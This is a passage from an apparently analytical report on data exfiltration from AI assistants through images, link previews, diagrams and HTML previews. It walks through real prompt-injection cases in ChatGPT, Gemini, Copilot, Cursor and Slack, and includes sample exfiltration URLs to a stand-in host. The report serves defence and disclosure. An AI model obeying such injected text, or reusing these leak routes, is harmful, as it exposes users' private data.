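| A reminder beside every reply | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupted the task when output was suspicious | 25.0% |

These figures are generous, because they include people who were unsure whether they had noticed anything. Only 2.7% could correctly describe an attack, even though nearly nine in ten participants had a degree and IT and technical workers were the largest group. Participants with technical expertise did slightly worse than the others with every type of warning.

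The comparison between warnings is less certain than the low overall rate, because Li and colleagues describe three groups of about 100 people in one place and groups of 183, 60 and 60 in another. No task tested whether people would click a link. A dialog that displays the exact address might work better than a general alert because it gives the user something specific to check. But the alert in this study appeared at the right moment and required a response, and three-quarters of the people who got it still reported nothing unusual.

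Studies of phishing suggest that people check addresses for signs of who sent a link. *Assessing AI-Generated vs. Human-Authored Spear Phishing SMS Attacks* (2024) reports that 16 interview participants (64%) mentioned the address when explaining why a text message seemed convincing or suspicious. One was more likely to click a link that contained their own name. Similarly, "Budget review" in an address might reassure the employee that the link was meant for her.

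*Evaluating Large Language Models' Capability to Launch Fully Automated Spear Phishing Campaigns* (2024) describes an accident that supports the same conclusion. The researchers sent 11 people an email in which a link meant to cover four words also covered the remaining 25 words of the message. One person mentioned the error, and eight clicked. Eleven people are too few for a reliable rate, and the fault was in the link's label, not its address, but it was much easier to see than an encoded meeting title.

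### Who is responsible for the click

Vendors can argue that a user who clicks a link has accepted the risk. Checkmarx tested how widely vendors would apply this argument with its October 2025 reports on links in Gemini and images in Copilot Chat. Neither report led to a fix.

Google gave two separate reasons, that a fix was infeasible and that the severity was low. It explained that tracking a bug commits product teams to monitoring and escalating it. Its reward programme covers only flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data". Google invited Checkmarx to explain anything Google had missed.

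Checkmarx called infeasibility "an acceptable answer", but said that Google should then warn users, because they would have to manage the risk themselves. This seems fair. Google is right that no filter can keep every useful link and stop every leak, but it already had a confirmation page in Colab, so it could have reduced the risk in Gemini without solving the whole problem.

Microsoft's case is harder to assess. It called the attack unreliable and dependent on unusual user actions. It also relied on a principle it calls Workplace Trust, which assumes that people review and trust the code they choose to run.

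That reasoning doesn't fit a leak through an image well, since the user in Checkmarx's demonstration ran no code to load it. Checkmarx printed the same letter, with the same dates, under its post on forged permission dialogs, which covers the Copilot Chat extension for VS Code. Those dialogs do ask users to approve code. Microsoft may have been answering one report that contained both findings, and writing mainly about the dialogs.

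In a late 2024 version of its severity scale, Microsoft rates prompt injection that exfiltrates another user's data as "Critical" if it needs no interaction and still "Important", one step lower, if it needs one or more clicks. The rating also depends on how easy an attack is to carry out, so Microsoft's decision on Copilot Chat may be consistent with the scale. The scale is only a guideline, and Microsoft later rated SearchLeak critical although the victim had to click a link.

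Checkmarx says that vendors of AI agents generally treat such behaviour as a risk that the user accepts. Anthropic gave Checkmarx a similar answer in August 2025, saying that forged dialogs in its coding assistant, Claude Code, were outside its threat model. Checkmarx objects that people can respond only to what the agent shows them, which an attacker's text can change. The developer who clicked "click here to reauthenticate" in Slack would have agreed only to log in again, but her click would have sent her key to a stranger.

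## Mobile apps, sister products and messaging apps that the fix did not reach

A vendor usually fixes an image or link leak in one app. The same model may also be available in a phone app, another of the vendor's products or another company's messaging app, each with its own renderer. OpenAI's Mac app, for example, still had an image leak nine months after the company started blocking it on the web.

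### Client-side and server-side checks

A client is the program on the user's side of the connection, such as a web page, a phone app or a desktop app. Suppose the employee's assistant has several clients, and the vendor adds an address check to the web page only. The server sends them all the same summary of conference venues, with the meeting title in an image address:

| Client | What happens to the image |
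|---|---|
| Web page with the check | The page asks the vendor's server about the address, gets a no and leaves the image out |
| Phone app without the check | The app loads the image and the title leaks |
| Phone app with the check, but not updated | The old version loads the image until the user installs the new one |
| Desktop app released a year later | The app loads the image unless its developers knew they had to add the check |

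A missing check causes no error. The app works normally and shows the picture, so its developers may not notice that anything is wrong.

If the server removes the address before sending the text, none of the four clients has anything to load. This also protects old versions and future apps. But the server has to recognise every form of address that any of the clients would load. Even if only the phone app turns HTML tags into images, the server has to look for HTML tags. A check in each renderer is therefore still useful in case the server misses one.

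Rehberger explains OpenAI's client-side check as a way to let replies keep streaming, which is plausible. The image address in the worked example has 56 characters and might arrive in a dozen or more fragments. A server-side check has to wait for the last fragment, and the server holds back any text that follows until then. A check in the page lets the text keep appearing while the page waits for the result.

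The delay would be short, though. If the model writes 200 characters a second, it finishes that address in about 0.3 seconds, and the check takes a little longer. The server could avoid this delay by sending a placeholder for the picture, continuing with the text, and sending the address later if it passes. A server-side check is therefore still possible with streaming, although a client-side one is easier to build.

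### When each ChatGPT app got the check

According to Embrace The Red, version 1.2023.347 of the iPhone app lacked the check in December 2023. Its *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* reports that the Mac and Android apps also lacked it in 2024.

| ChatGPT app | Known to lack the check | Check added |
|---|---|---|
| Web | Before December 2023 | December 2023 |
| iPhone | December 2023 | Rehberger gives no date |
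| Android | 2024, and probably December 2023 | Rehberger gives no date |
| Mac | June 2024 | September 2024, in version 1.2024.247 |

The phone apps may not have gained the protection until the summer of 2025, when OpenAI seems to have moved the check to its own servers. That move would have protected every app at once, but OpenAI may have added a check to the phone apps earlier.

The gap in the Mac app became more serious in 2024, when OpenAI gave ChatGPT a memory that carries information from one chat into later ones. Rehberger used it to make an image leak permanent:

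1. The user asks ChatGPT in the Mac app about a web page or document that contains the attacker's text.

2. The text gets ChatGPT to save a new memory, which is an instruction to add an image to its answers and put the conversation into the image's address.

3. ChatGPT includes the memory in every new chat, so the instruction still works after the user has closed the first one.

4. The Mac app loads each image without checking its address. The attacker's server receives what the user types and what ChatGPT answers, and the user sees nothing because the image is invisible.

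Samoilenko's persistent attack in 2023 affected later answers in the same conversation. The attack stored in memory continued until the user found and deleted the memory or OpenAI blocked the image.

ChatGPT ties memories to the user's account rather than to one app, so an instruction planted through the website, where the check would have blocked the image, would presumably have started leaking data when the same user opened the Mac app. If so, the web check only partly protected anyone who also used another app.

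Rehberger first reported in May 2024 that a website could plant false memories. OpenAI closed that report as a model safety issue, not a security one. In June he sent a demonstration of the full leak. His injected text stopped working at some point in July, but he soon found wording that worked. About three months after the demonstration, OpenAI fixed the Mac app with an update that blocked the leak whatever the wording.

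The fix did not stop websites from planting memories. Rehberger advises users to review their stored memories regularly and delete any they don't recognise. The desktop app's HTML preview later turned out to have its own leak.

### Google AI Studio: the leak returns through HTML

Google had fixed image leaks in Generative AI Studio, Bard and Colab by the end of January 2024. Later that year it fixed one in Google AI Studio, a separate tool where developers try out its Gemini models. When Rehberger tested AI Studio again that summer, he could still make it load an outside image.

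He had occasional success with markdown tricks, then found that he could have the model write an HTML image tag. Embrace The Red calls this either a regression, meaning that a later change had undone the fix, or a bypass. Rehberger thought the HTML route might have been open all along. A bypass seems likelier, since a fix aimed at markdown could easily have missed HTML, but Google did not say which it was.

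Rehberger's demonstration used a set of employee performance reviews. One employee had hidden instructions in their own review, and someone then uploaded all the reviews for analysis. For each file, the model wrote a separate image address with the file's name and a 60-word summary of its contents as parameters. The browser then sent the names and summaries to Rehberger's server, one file at a time. Using separate addresses let him extract much more data than one address could hold. In a second demonstration, the instructions appeared in the frames of a video.

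Private data may have been at risk in AI Studio, even though developers use it mostly for testing. At the time, it was the only place where people could try Google's newest experimental model. Willison (2024), in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo*, thought this made it more likely that people were using it to process real data.

Google's security team had not given Rehberger a date for a fix, so he tagged Logan Kilpatrick of Google in a public post on X. Within 24 hours AI Studio was displaying image tags as text. This closed the HTML route, but like earlier fixes, it changed only one product's renderer.

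### GeminiJack: the same exit in Gemini Enterprise

In December 2025 Noma Labs, which had found the Salesforce flaw, disclosed another image leak in a Google product and called it GeminiJack. The leak affected Gemini Enterprise, which lets employees search their company's email, calendars and documents. It had also affected Vertex AI Search, according to *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration* (Paganini, 2025).

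SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* describes the attack. The attacker sends an employee an email, calendar invitation or shared document. When the employee later searches for something related, Gemini Enterprise retrieves the attacker's text along with genuine results. The model follows instructions in that text to run a second search, such as one for emails from the sales department, and put the results at the end of an image address. When the browser loads the image, it sends those results to the attacker.

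The attack could reach a lot of data because, for every query, Gemini Enterprise has access to all the sources a company chose in advance, as Noma explains in Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data*. Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, told TechNadu that Google "didn't filter HTML output". The researchers had extracted long emails this way but had not tested how much data a single address could hold.

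Noma reported the flaw in June 2025. That same month, Google said that Gemini's sanitizer did not render outside images. Tenable's research, which SiliconANGLE (2025) covered on 30 September, also found that Gemini no longer rendered image markdown as it once had. All three accounts may be correct. Google may have been describing its main Gemini products, while Gemini Enterprise, which shared the name, evidently lacked the same protection.

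Google had fixed GeminiJack by November 2025 but did not publish the technical details. Noma wrote that the fix dealt with how the system confused instructions with retrieved content. Levi told SC Media that he did not know whether Google had cleaned the content, changed how it parsed text or reorganised the search system.

The difference matters to customers because an attacker with better wording might get the model to write an image tag again. The browser might load that image if Google only changed how retrieved text reaches the model, but not if Gemini Enterprise also stopped displaying outside images.

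Google repaired these five products separately over more than two years:

| Google product | Leak reported | Known fix |
|---|---|---|
| Generative AI Studio | August 2023 | It stopped rendering images and links |
| Bard | September 2023 | Apparently a filter for addresses with inserted data |
| Colab's assistant | November 2023 | Google closed the report as fixed but links still worked |
| AI Studio, HTML route | Summer 2024 | It displays image tags as text |
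| Gemini Enterprise | June 2025 | Google did not disclose it |

If every product team had used a shared rendering component with one set of rules, much of this work would have been avoided. The central policy engine Google described for Workspace in 2026 is a step in that direction. But products need to display different things, and a rule strict enough for a developer tool may remove pictures that an office assistant needs to show.

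### How link previews remove the click

When an agent posts its answer in Slack or Telegram, the agent's developer does not control how it is displayed. These apps fetch a preview of any link in a message, usually a title, a short description and a picture. Slack calls this unfurling. Unfurling makes a plain link as dangerous as an image, as Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explained in August 2024.

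Suppose the employee talks to her assistant through Slack, and the hidden text on the page about conference venues makes it add a link with her meeting title in the address. As soon as the assistant posts its answer, Slack's server requests the page in order to build a preview. The attacker's log then shows something like this:

```
198.51.100.44 [05/Dec/2026:10:14:03 +0000]
"GET /?title=Budget%20review HTTP/1.1" 200 "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0 ..."
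```

As with an image proxy, the attacker sees Slack's network address instead of the employee's but still receives the title. Slack can send the request before she reads the message. The model doesn't need to write markdown, because Slack recognises a bare address that starts with "http://" or "https://".

Most of the defences in a vendor's own chat window do not apply when another company's app displays the answer. A Content Security Policy covers only the page it comes with, and a check built into the vendor's app does not run in the other app. A check on the agent's server still works if it runs before the agent posts the message.

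### PromptArmor's test of agents and apps

In February 2026 PromptArmor set up a public website where people could test their own combinations of agent and messaging app. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that the site recorded each preview request and the data in its address. Testers could claim a log entry and name the agent and app that produced it. They could also report combinations that did not fetch a preview.

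PromptArmor reports that OpenClaw, an agent that people run themselves, is exposed by default when used through Telegram. It also published charts of the riskiest combinations of agent and messaging app, and of the programs that fetched the most previews, such as Slack's and Telegram's. The charts relied on tests by volunteers, so a combination could rank high simply because many people had tried it. The results are good evidence that such leaks happen, but they do not show how often each product leaks.

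OpenClaw users can turn the previews off with one line in the agent's settings:

```
channels: { telegram: { linkPreview: false } }
```

PromptArmor says its site stopped receiving data once this setting was in place. Previews are still on by default, according to OpenClaw's documentation page *Telegram*. So users are protected only if they have heard of the problem and changed the setting.

PromptArmor thinks messaging companies should let developers control link previews, and agent developers should use those controls or pass the choice on to their users. It also proposes that messaging apps allow separate preview settings for each channel, so that a company could turn previews off where an agent posts and keep them on elsewhere.

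### Slack's two preview settings

Slack lets a developer switch previews off for each message. A message with the link from the example would look like this:

```
{
  "text": "Venue comparison: https://pictures.example/?title=Budget%20review",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

The first setting covers pages that are mainly text, and the second covers images, video and audio. The first is not enough on its own, even for an ordinary link. Slack's servers have to fetch an address to find out which kind of content it leads to, as Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains, and that fetch leaks the data.

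| `unfurl_links` | `unfurl_media` | Does Slack contact the outside server? |
|---|---|---|
| Not set | Not set | Yes |
| `false` | Not set | Probably, to find out whether the content is media |
| Not set | `false` | Probably, to find out whether the content is text |
| `false` | `false` | No |

Slack states the last result directly. The two middle rows follow from its explanation, although it doesn't discuss those cases.

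The documentation is inconsistent about what happens when a developer sets neither. It says that Slack unfurls all links in messages from apps by default, but in one of its examples, a link to a text page unfurls only if the developer asks for it. Rehberger's test supports the general statement. He posted a plain link through a webhook, a simple way for a program to send a message to Slack, and his server recorded Slack's visit. A missing preview would not prove that Slack had sent no request, since Slack may have fetched the page without showing a preview.

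Slack also never unfurls links whose visible text is just part of the address, such as "pictures.example". This is little help against an attacker, who can have the model choose different text.

Slack now advises developers to "consider disabling link unfurls" for messages from a language model, which leaves the decision to each developer. It would be safer for Slack to turn link previews off by default for any app that posts a model's text, but Slack would need a way to identify those apps.

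### A Slack connector that nobody will patch

Developers can easily miss the settings. Anthropic's own Slack connector, which let an agent read and post Slack messages, left previews on. Anthropic had published the connector as an example when it introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to outside tools.

Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* explains why this was easy to overlook. Every link the agent posted made Slack contact an outside server, so data could leave the company even through a private channel. But a company that allowed the agent to post only in one private channel could reasonably conclude that those posts didn't need approval, because nobody outside the company could read them.

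In one of Rehberger's demonstrations, a document got Claude's desktop app to copy the latest message from one Slack channel into a link and post the link in a different, private channel. In another, invisible characters in a source file got Claude Code to read a developer's API key from a settings file and post it the same way. If the link was to an image, up to three of Slack's programs, including its image proxy, requested it, so the data could leak several times.

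Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Two days later Anthropic archived the connector, so it would no longer receive security fixes, though he could not tell whether the two events were connected. People were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week when he published his advisory. Adding Slack's two settings to the code that posts and replies to messages fixes the flaw, but each company still using the connector has to make the change itself.

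He suggests that connectors turn previews off by default and perhaps let companies allow them for selected domains. Such a list would need the same care as a list of permitted image hosts.

### Copilot Cowork's messages to its own user

A vendor can have the same problem when it owns both apps. In May 2026 PromptArmor described a leak in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that carries out office tasks and can send messages through Teams and Outlook. Microsoft said in its documentation that the agent asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams, but PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that the agent did not ask before messaging its own user.

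Messages sent under that exception go only to the user herself, but they could still leak her data because Teams and Outlook loaded outside images in them. In PromptArmor's attack, the agent put links to the user's files into image addresses and sent them to her in a Teams message. When she opened it, Teams requested the images from the attacker's server, which received the links. Anyone with such a link could download the file without logging in, so one short image address could expose a whole document.

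The attacker's text was five lines in an 81-line skill file, a set of instructions that users can add to the agent. The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials. The user could not have spotted it by checking Cowork's record of the task, which showed that the agent had sent a Teams message but not what the message contained. A scheduled task could send a new message every week without the user being there.

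PromptArmor treated this as a risk in the product's design rather than a single bug, and advised administrators to limit which files the agent can access and to block downloads of sensitive ones. Blocking downloads also stops people from opening those files in Word or Excel, which is a serious drawback for many offices. Microsoft could instead make Teams and Outlook block external images in any message an agent wrote, including messages to the agent's own user.

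## Diagrams, HTML previews and other content drawn by a separate renderer

A chat window often contains several renderers. One turns markdown into formatted text, while others draw diagrams, display formulas, plot graphs or run small web pages the model wrote. Each has its own syntax for images and links, so a vendor can block every markdown image and still have the same leak in a diagram.

| Renderer | What the model writes | What can send a request |
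|---|---|---|
| Markdown | Text with punctuation marks | Images, and links after a click |
| Diagrams | A list of boxes and arrows | Images, styles and links inside the drawing |
| Mathematics | A formula in LaTeX notation | Images and links, if the app allows them |
| HTML preview | A complete web page | Images, fonts, scripts, forms and new windows |

KaTeX, a popular library for displaying formulas, disables its image and link commands by default. Not all renderers are this restrictive, and vendors keep adding new ones. ChatGPT gained an HTML preview in February 2026, and OpenAI's *New ways to learn math and science in ChatGPT* (2026) announced interactive visual explanations in March.

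### Why a markdown filter misses a diagram

Mermaid is an open-source tool that draws diagrams from short text descriptions. To use it in a chat, the model writes a code block, which markdown normally displays exactly as written, and labels it "mermaid":

```
graph LR
    Dates --> Venue
    Venue --> Booking
```

The app passes these lines to Mermaid, which draws three boxes joined by arrows. Depending on the app's settings, a box can also contain an HTML image tag, have its own styles or act as a link.

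If the employee's assistant adds this diagram to its summary of conference venues, a sanitizer that parses the markdown gets the following tree:

```
reply
  paragraph
    text: "The three venues compare as follows."
  code block, labelled "mermaid"
    text: "graph LR ..."
```

The tree would contain no image or link even if the diagram did. A good sanitizer doesn't change code blocks, but Mermaid interprets the text afterwards and can turn it into an image that the browser loads.

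### Cursor: an image inside a box

Rehberger found that Mermaid diagrams in Cursor, a code editor with an AI assistant, could load images from an outside server. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes an attack in which a short program included a comment instructing the assistant to draw a diagram whenever it explained the file, and to put an image with private text in its address in one of the boxes.

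In one demonstration, Cursor searched the developer's project for API keys and sent one from a settings file to Rehberger's server. In another, it sent the memories it had stored about the developer. The developer only had to ask Cursor to explain the file. Rehberger also noted that the diagram appears only when finished, so the user can't see a long address full of data while the model is writing.

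He reported the flaw on 30 June 2025. Cursor resolved it a week later and released the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July. But MITRE's *Cursor* (2025), a second official record published in October (CVE-2025-61589), mentions bypasses that the first fix did not cover. Cursor fixed those in version 1.7. The record does not describe the bypasses, but they show that repairing a renderer one syntax at a time is hard.

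The two records also give different severity scores. The first, MITRE's *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025, CVE-2025-54132), gives 4.4 out of 10, and the second gives 5.9. The lower score is based on an attacker who already has a high level of access, and the higher one on an attacker who has none. The second case is more realistic, since the attacker's text could be in any source file or web page that the developer asks about.

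### Microsoft 365 Copilot: a fake login button

Security researcher Adam Logue used a Mermaid diagram to steal emails through Microsoft 365 Copilot, in an attack made public in October 2025. The attack began when a user asked Copilot to summarise a spreadsheet. The attacker's instructions, in white text on several sheets, changed the task in stages, according to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*.

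Copilot then fetched the user's recent emails and encoded them in hexadecimal, according to daily.dev's summary of Logue's post. It drew a diagram that looked like a login button and put the encoded emails in the button's link. Clicking the button sent them to the attacker's server. CyberMaterial (2025) adds that the user then saw a mock Microsoft 365 login screen, which suggested that they had to log in to see the summary.

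This resembles the "reauthenticate" link in Slack AI, but Mermaid's styles made the trick more convincing. In markdown, an attacker can choose a link's words but not its shape or colour.

Logue may have needed a click because Copilot's Content Security Policy restricted images but not links. Cursor loaded an image directly from Rehberger's server, so it evidently had no comparable restriction on images.

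Microsoft responded by disabling links in Copilot's diagrams. This works no matter how the model writes the link, and few people need to click on a diagram. Logue received no reward because Microsoft 365 Copilot was outside Microsoft's bounty programme at the time.

### What a sandboxed preview isolates

An HTML preview is riskier than a diagram because it can run JavaScript, the programming language of web pages. Vendors therefore put it in an iframe, a frame that displays one web page inside another:

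```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts"
        src="https://preview.example/page"></iframe>
```

The frame's separate host name provides part of the isolation. Browsers do not let code from preview.example read a page on chat.company.example, or the cookies and other data which that site has stored. The `sandbox` attribute takes away further abilities, and the developer gives back only those the preview needs:

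| Permission | What it lets the preview do |
|---|---|
| `allow-scripts` | Run JavaScript |
| `allow-forms` | Submit forms |
| `allow-popups` | Open new windows |
| `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` | Open new windows without the frame's restrictions |
| `allow-top-navigation` | Replace the whole chat page with another page |

None of these settings stops the preview from loading an image from pictures.example. The model may also have written "Budget review" into the preview's code, in which case the preview doesn't need to read anything from the chat page. To prevent a leak, the vendor has to restrict the preview's network requests as well.

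Checking the code before the preview runs is not enough, because JavaScript can assemble an address from fragments at runtime. The full address may never appear in the model's reply.

*Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) describes a ChatGPT preview that runs inside two nested sandboxed frames. When the preview tries to load something from outside, ChatGPT holds the request until the user approves it in a dialog. This protects the user only if every kind of request triggers the dialog and the user can recognise a dangerous one.

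### Copilot's preview: a font instead of an image

Microsoft 365 Copilot gained an HTML preview in the autumn of 2025. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes how Rehberger got data out of it (CVE-2026-24299). The preview removed image tags, so he asked Copilot to write a page that used as many ways of loading an external file as possible. The one that worked was a background image set in the page's CSS.

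A Content Security Policy still limited where background pictures could come from. But Copilot runs inside Word, Excel, SharePoint and other products, and the policy varied by product. Rehberger found long lists of permitted hosts, including subdomains of azureedge.net, some of which belong to Microsoft's customers. Some entries contained what looked like employees' user names, which suggested to him that individual employees had added their own domains.

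Web pages can also load fonts, which have their own rule in a Content Security Policy. Because Copilot's rule for fonts was looser than its rule for images, Rehberger could load a font directly from his own server, with stolen text in the font's address. This worked in many of the products that included Copilot, so he did not need to look for a weak host in each list.

Copilot showed the page's code first, and the browser loaded nothing until the user switched to the preview. So Rehberger also used his injected text to ask Copilot to show the preview, which it reliably did. In his demonstration, a user opened a shared Word document and typed only "hi there" to Copilot. Copilot found an email with the subject "The Code" and put the email's contents into the font's address.

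In another version, a document planted an instruction in Copilot's memory. Whenever the user later pasted in a password or code, Copilot made a new preview and leaked the secret through the font. Microsoft reported this version fixed on 6 December 2025. Rehberger reported the font leak itself on 16 October, and Microsoft recorded the fix on 5 March 2026.

### ChatGPT's preview: a popup outside the sandbox

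Check Point found a gap in ChatGPT's preview that also defeated Lockdown Mode, OpenAI's optional setting for blocking ways to send data out. The gap was in how ChatGPT handled new windows.

Web pages open new windows by calling `window.open`. ChatGPT had replaced this function in the preview with a version that asked the user for approval. But a page can create another frame inside itself, and the browser gives every frame its own copy of the original function. Code in the preview could call that copy to open a window without asking the user.

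The sandbox should then have blocked the new window, but both of its popup permissions were on. The window opened outside the sandbox, so neither the preview's restrictions nor Lockdown Mode applied to it. An attacker could deliver the code through a malicious prompt, a shared chat or a custom GPT (a version of ChatGPT that follows its creator's instructions).

According to Duggan, Check Point demonstrated four uses:

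- A custom GPT sent the whole chat history to an outside server while the user talked to it. In the ChatGPT Classic desktop app, the new window opened without a click.
- A window with ChatGPT's icon offered a fake update containing malware. Desktop users had to click to download it, but a browser could start the download automatically.
- The attacker signed the user out of the desktop app and displayed a false login page.
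- A popup showed other phishing content that the user might take for part of ChatGPT.

If the employee had mentioned her budget review to such a GPT in the desktop app, the GPT's creator could have received the title without her doing anything more, even with Lockdown Mode on.

On 18 September 2026 OpenAI told Check Point that it had removed both popup permissions from the outer frame. Check Point retested the attack, found that it no longer worked, and published its findings on 5 November. It did not report any real attacks. The fix works because the browser now blocks every new window, whichever copy of the function the code calls. OpenAI's earlier defence was written in JavaScript and covered only one copy.

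### A shared conversation that opened the victim's account

A week before Check Point's disclosure, the security company Parameter published a more serious flaw involving the same preview. Parameter's code got into the main ChatGPT page, where it could use the victim's account, while Check Point's code only escaped into a separate window.

Goyal (2026), in *Do the Math*, explains how a public conversation, shared through ChatGPT's normal feature, could do this:

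1. The victim opens the shared conversation while signed in to ChatGPT. It contains a graph, which loads a library called MathLive into the main page. MathLive starts listening for messages about its on-screen keyboard.

2. The conversation also contains an HTML preview. The preview cannot read the main page, but browsers let frames send each other messages. It sends MathLive a new keyboard layout that contains the attacker's HTML.

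3. MathLive accepts the layout without checking who sent it. A further message makes the keyboard appear, which inserts the attacker's HTML into the main page.

4. The browser does not run scripts inserted this way, so the HTML creates a new frame. The frame has no sandbox, and the browser treats it as part of chatgpt.com because the main page created it.

5. ChatGPT's Content Security Policy blocks code written directly in the new frame but allows scripts from YouTube. One YouTube service copied text from a request into a script it sent back, even when it rejected the request. The researchers used this to run their own code.

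The code listed the victim's conversations, opened one the victim had never shared, and sent part of it to the researchers' server. The researchers tested this between separate accounts, not on real users. *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026) says the data could leave through an image address. ChatGPT's check on image addresses might not apply, because the attacker's code made the request.

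The researchers took several attempts to turn this into a single link. Their first version needed the victim to use a ChatGPT app that the researchers controlled. They then tried putting the preview in an attached file, but the shared copy of the conversation left out the graph, so MathLive never loaded. They solved the problem by writing both the graph and the preview into the conversation.

In the most reliable version, the victim still had to press the Preview button. The researchers later got the preview to open by itself, and the attack ran about 4.5 seconds after the victim opened the link. They repeated this version three times in a separate account.

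The two flaws compare as follows:

| | Check Point's popup | Parameter's shared conversation |
|---|---|---|
| Where the attacker's code ran | A new window outside the sandbox | The main ChatGPT page |
| What it could reach | The current chat, and users it could deceive | Everything in the victim's account |
| Least the victim had to do | Talk to a malicious GPT in the desktop app | Open a link while signed in |
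| OpenAI's repair | Removed the popup permissions | Made the page reject the keyboard messages |
| Date of the repair | 18 September 2026 | 26 October 2026 |

Parameter's attack also didn't need the victim's model to follow any instructions. The attacker's code read the private chats directly, so neither a better-trained model nor a filter on its replies would have prevented the theft.

The researchers reported the flaw on 18 October. The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026) reports that OpenAI raised the flaw's rating to P1, the most serious category, after reproducing the theft of a private chat. OpenAI paid $5,000, which Willison called "a bit cheap" for such a serious flaw.

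### Protecting every renderer at once

A vendor could avoid much of this repair work by restricting the whole window instead of each syntax. It would need to apply a network policy to every renderer, run each renderer in its own sandboxed frame, and keep new features off until both protections cover them.

For a preview or diagram, the network policy could be as short as this:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none';
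    script-src 'unsafe-inline'; style-src 'unsafe-inline';
    img-src data:
```

This allows scripts and styles written in the page, and embedded images, but blocks anything from an outside server, including fonts and pictures.

A frame whose HTML is part of the main page inherits that page's content security policy, but a frame loaded from another host follows the policy that host sends. ChatGPT's main page blocks inline scripts, which most previews need, so inheriting its policy would break them. The vendor has to send a policy from the preview's own host that allows inline scripts but restricts outside servers at least as strictly as the main page does.

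Neither the network policy nor the frame would have stopped all five attacks alone:

| Attack | Network policy with no outside hosts | Separate frame that cannot open windows or leave the chat |
|---|---|---|
| Image in Cursor's diagram | Stops it | Does not stop it |
| Link in Copilot's diagram | Does not stop it | Stops it |
| Font in Copilot's preview | Stops it, if every product uses the policy | Does not stop it |
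| Popup from ChatGPT's preview | Does not stop it | Stops it |
| Shared ChatGPT conversation | Blocks the YouTube script, but attacker's HTML still enters the page | Stops it, if the graph has its own frame |

The graph in the last row matters because it loaded MathLive into the main page. If MathLive had run in a frame with a separate host name, it might still have accepted the attacker's layout, but the resulting HTML could not have accessed the victim's account. OpenAI had isolated the preview, which it knew to be dangerous, but not the graph, because it seemed harmless. The Hacker News notes that blocking only the YouTube script would still have let an attacker reach the main page.

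Keeping a feature off by default works only if an attacker's text cannot turn it on. Copilot's preview was closed by default, but the model opened it when asked. ChatGPT's preview normally waited for a click, but the creator of a shared conversation could make it open automatically. Only the user or an administrator should therefore be able to turn on such a feature. Lockdown Mode would be a natural place for this setting, since it already turns off whole features such as deep research.

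These restrictions have little effect on diagrams and formulas, which rarely need anything from outside. They limit previews more, because many small web pages use maps, outside photographs or shared code libraries. A vendor could supply the most common libraries from its own host, provided that the host serves only fixed files. The YouTube service was dangerous because its script contained text that the requester had chosen.

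The rule about products matters most for a vendor like Microsoft, whose assistant appears inside many other products. Rehberger argues that anyone who embeds an assistant in another page needs to know which side is responsible for preventing leaks. If the assistant depends on the surrounding page's Content Security Policy, moving it unchanged to a page with a weaker policy removes the protection.
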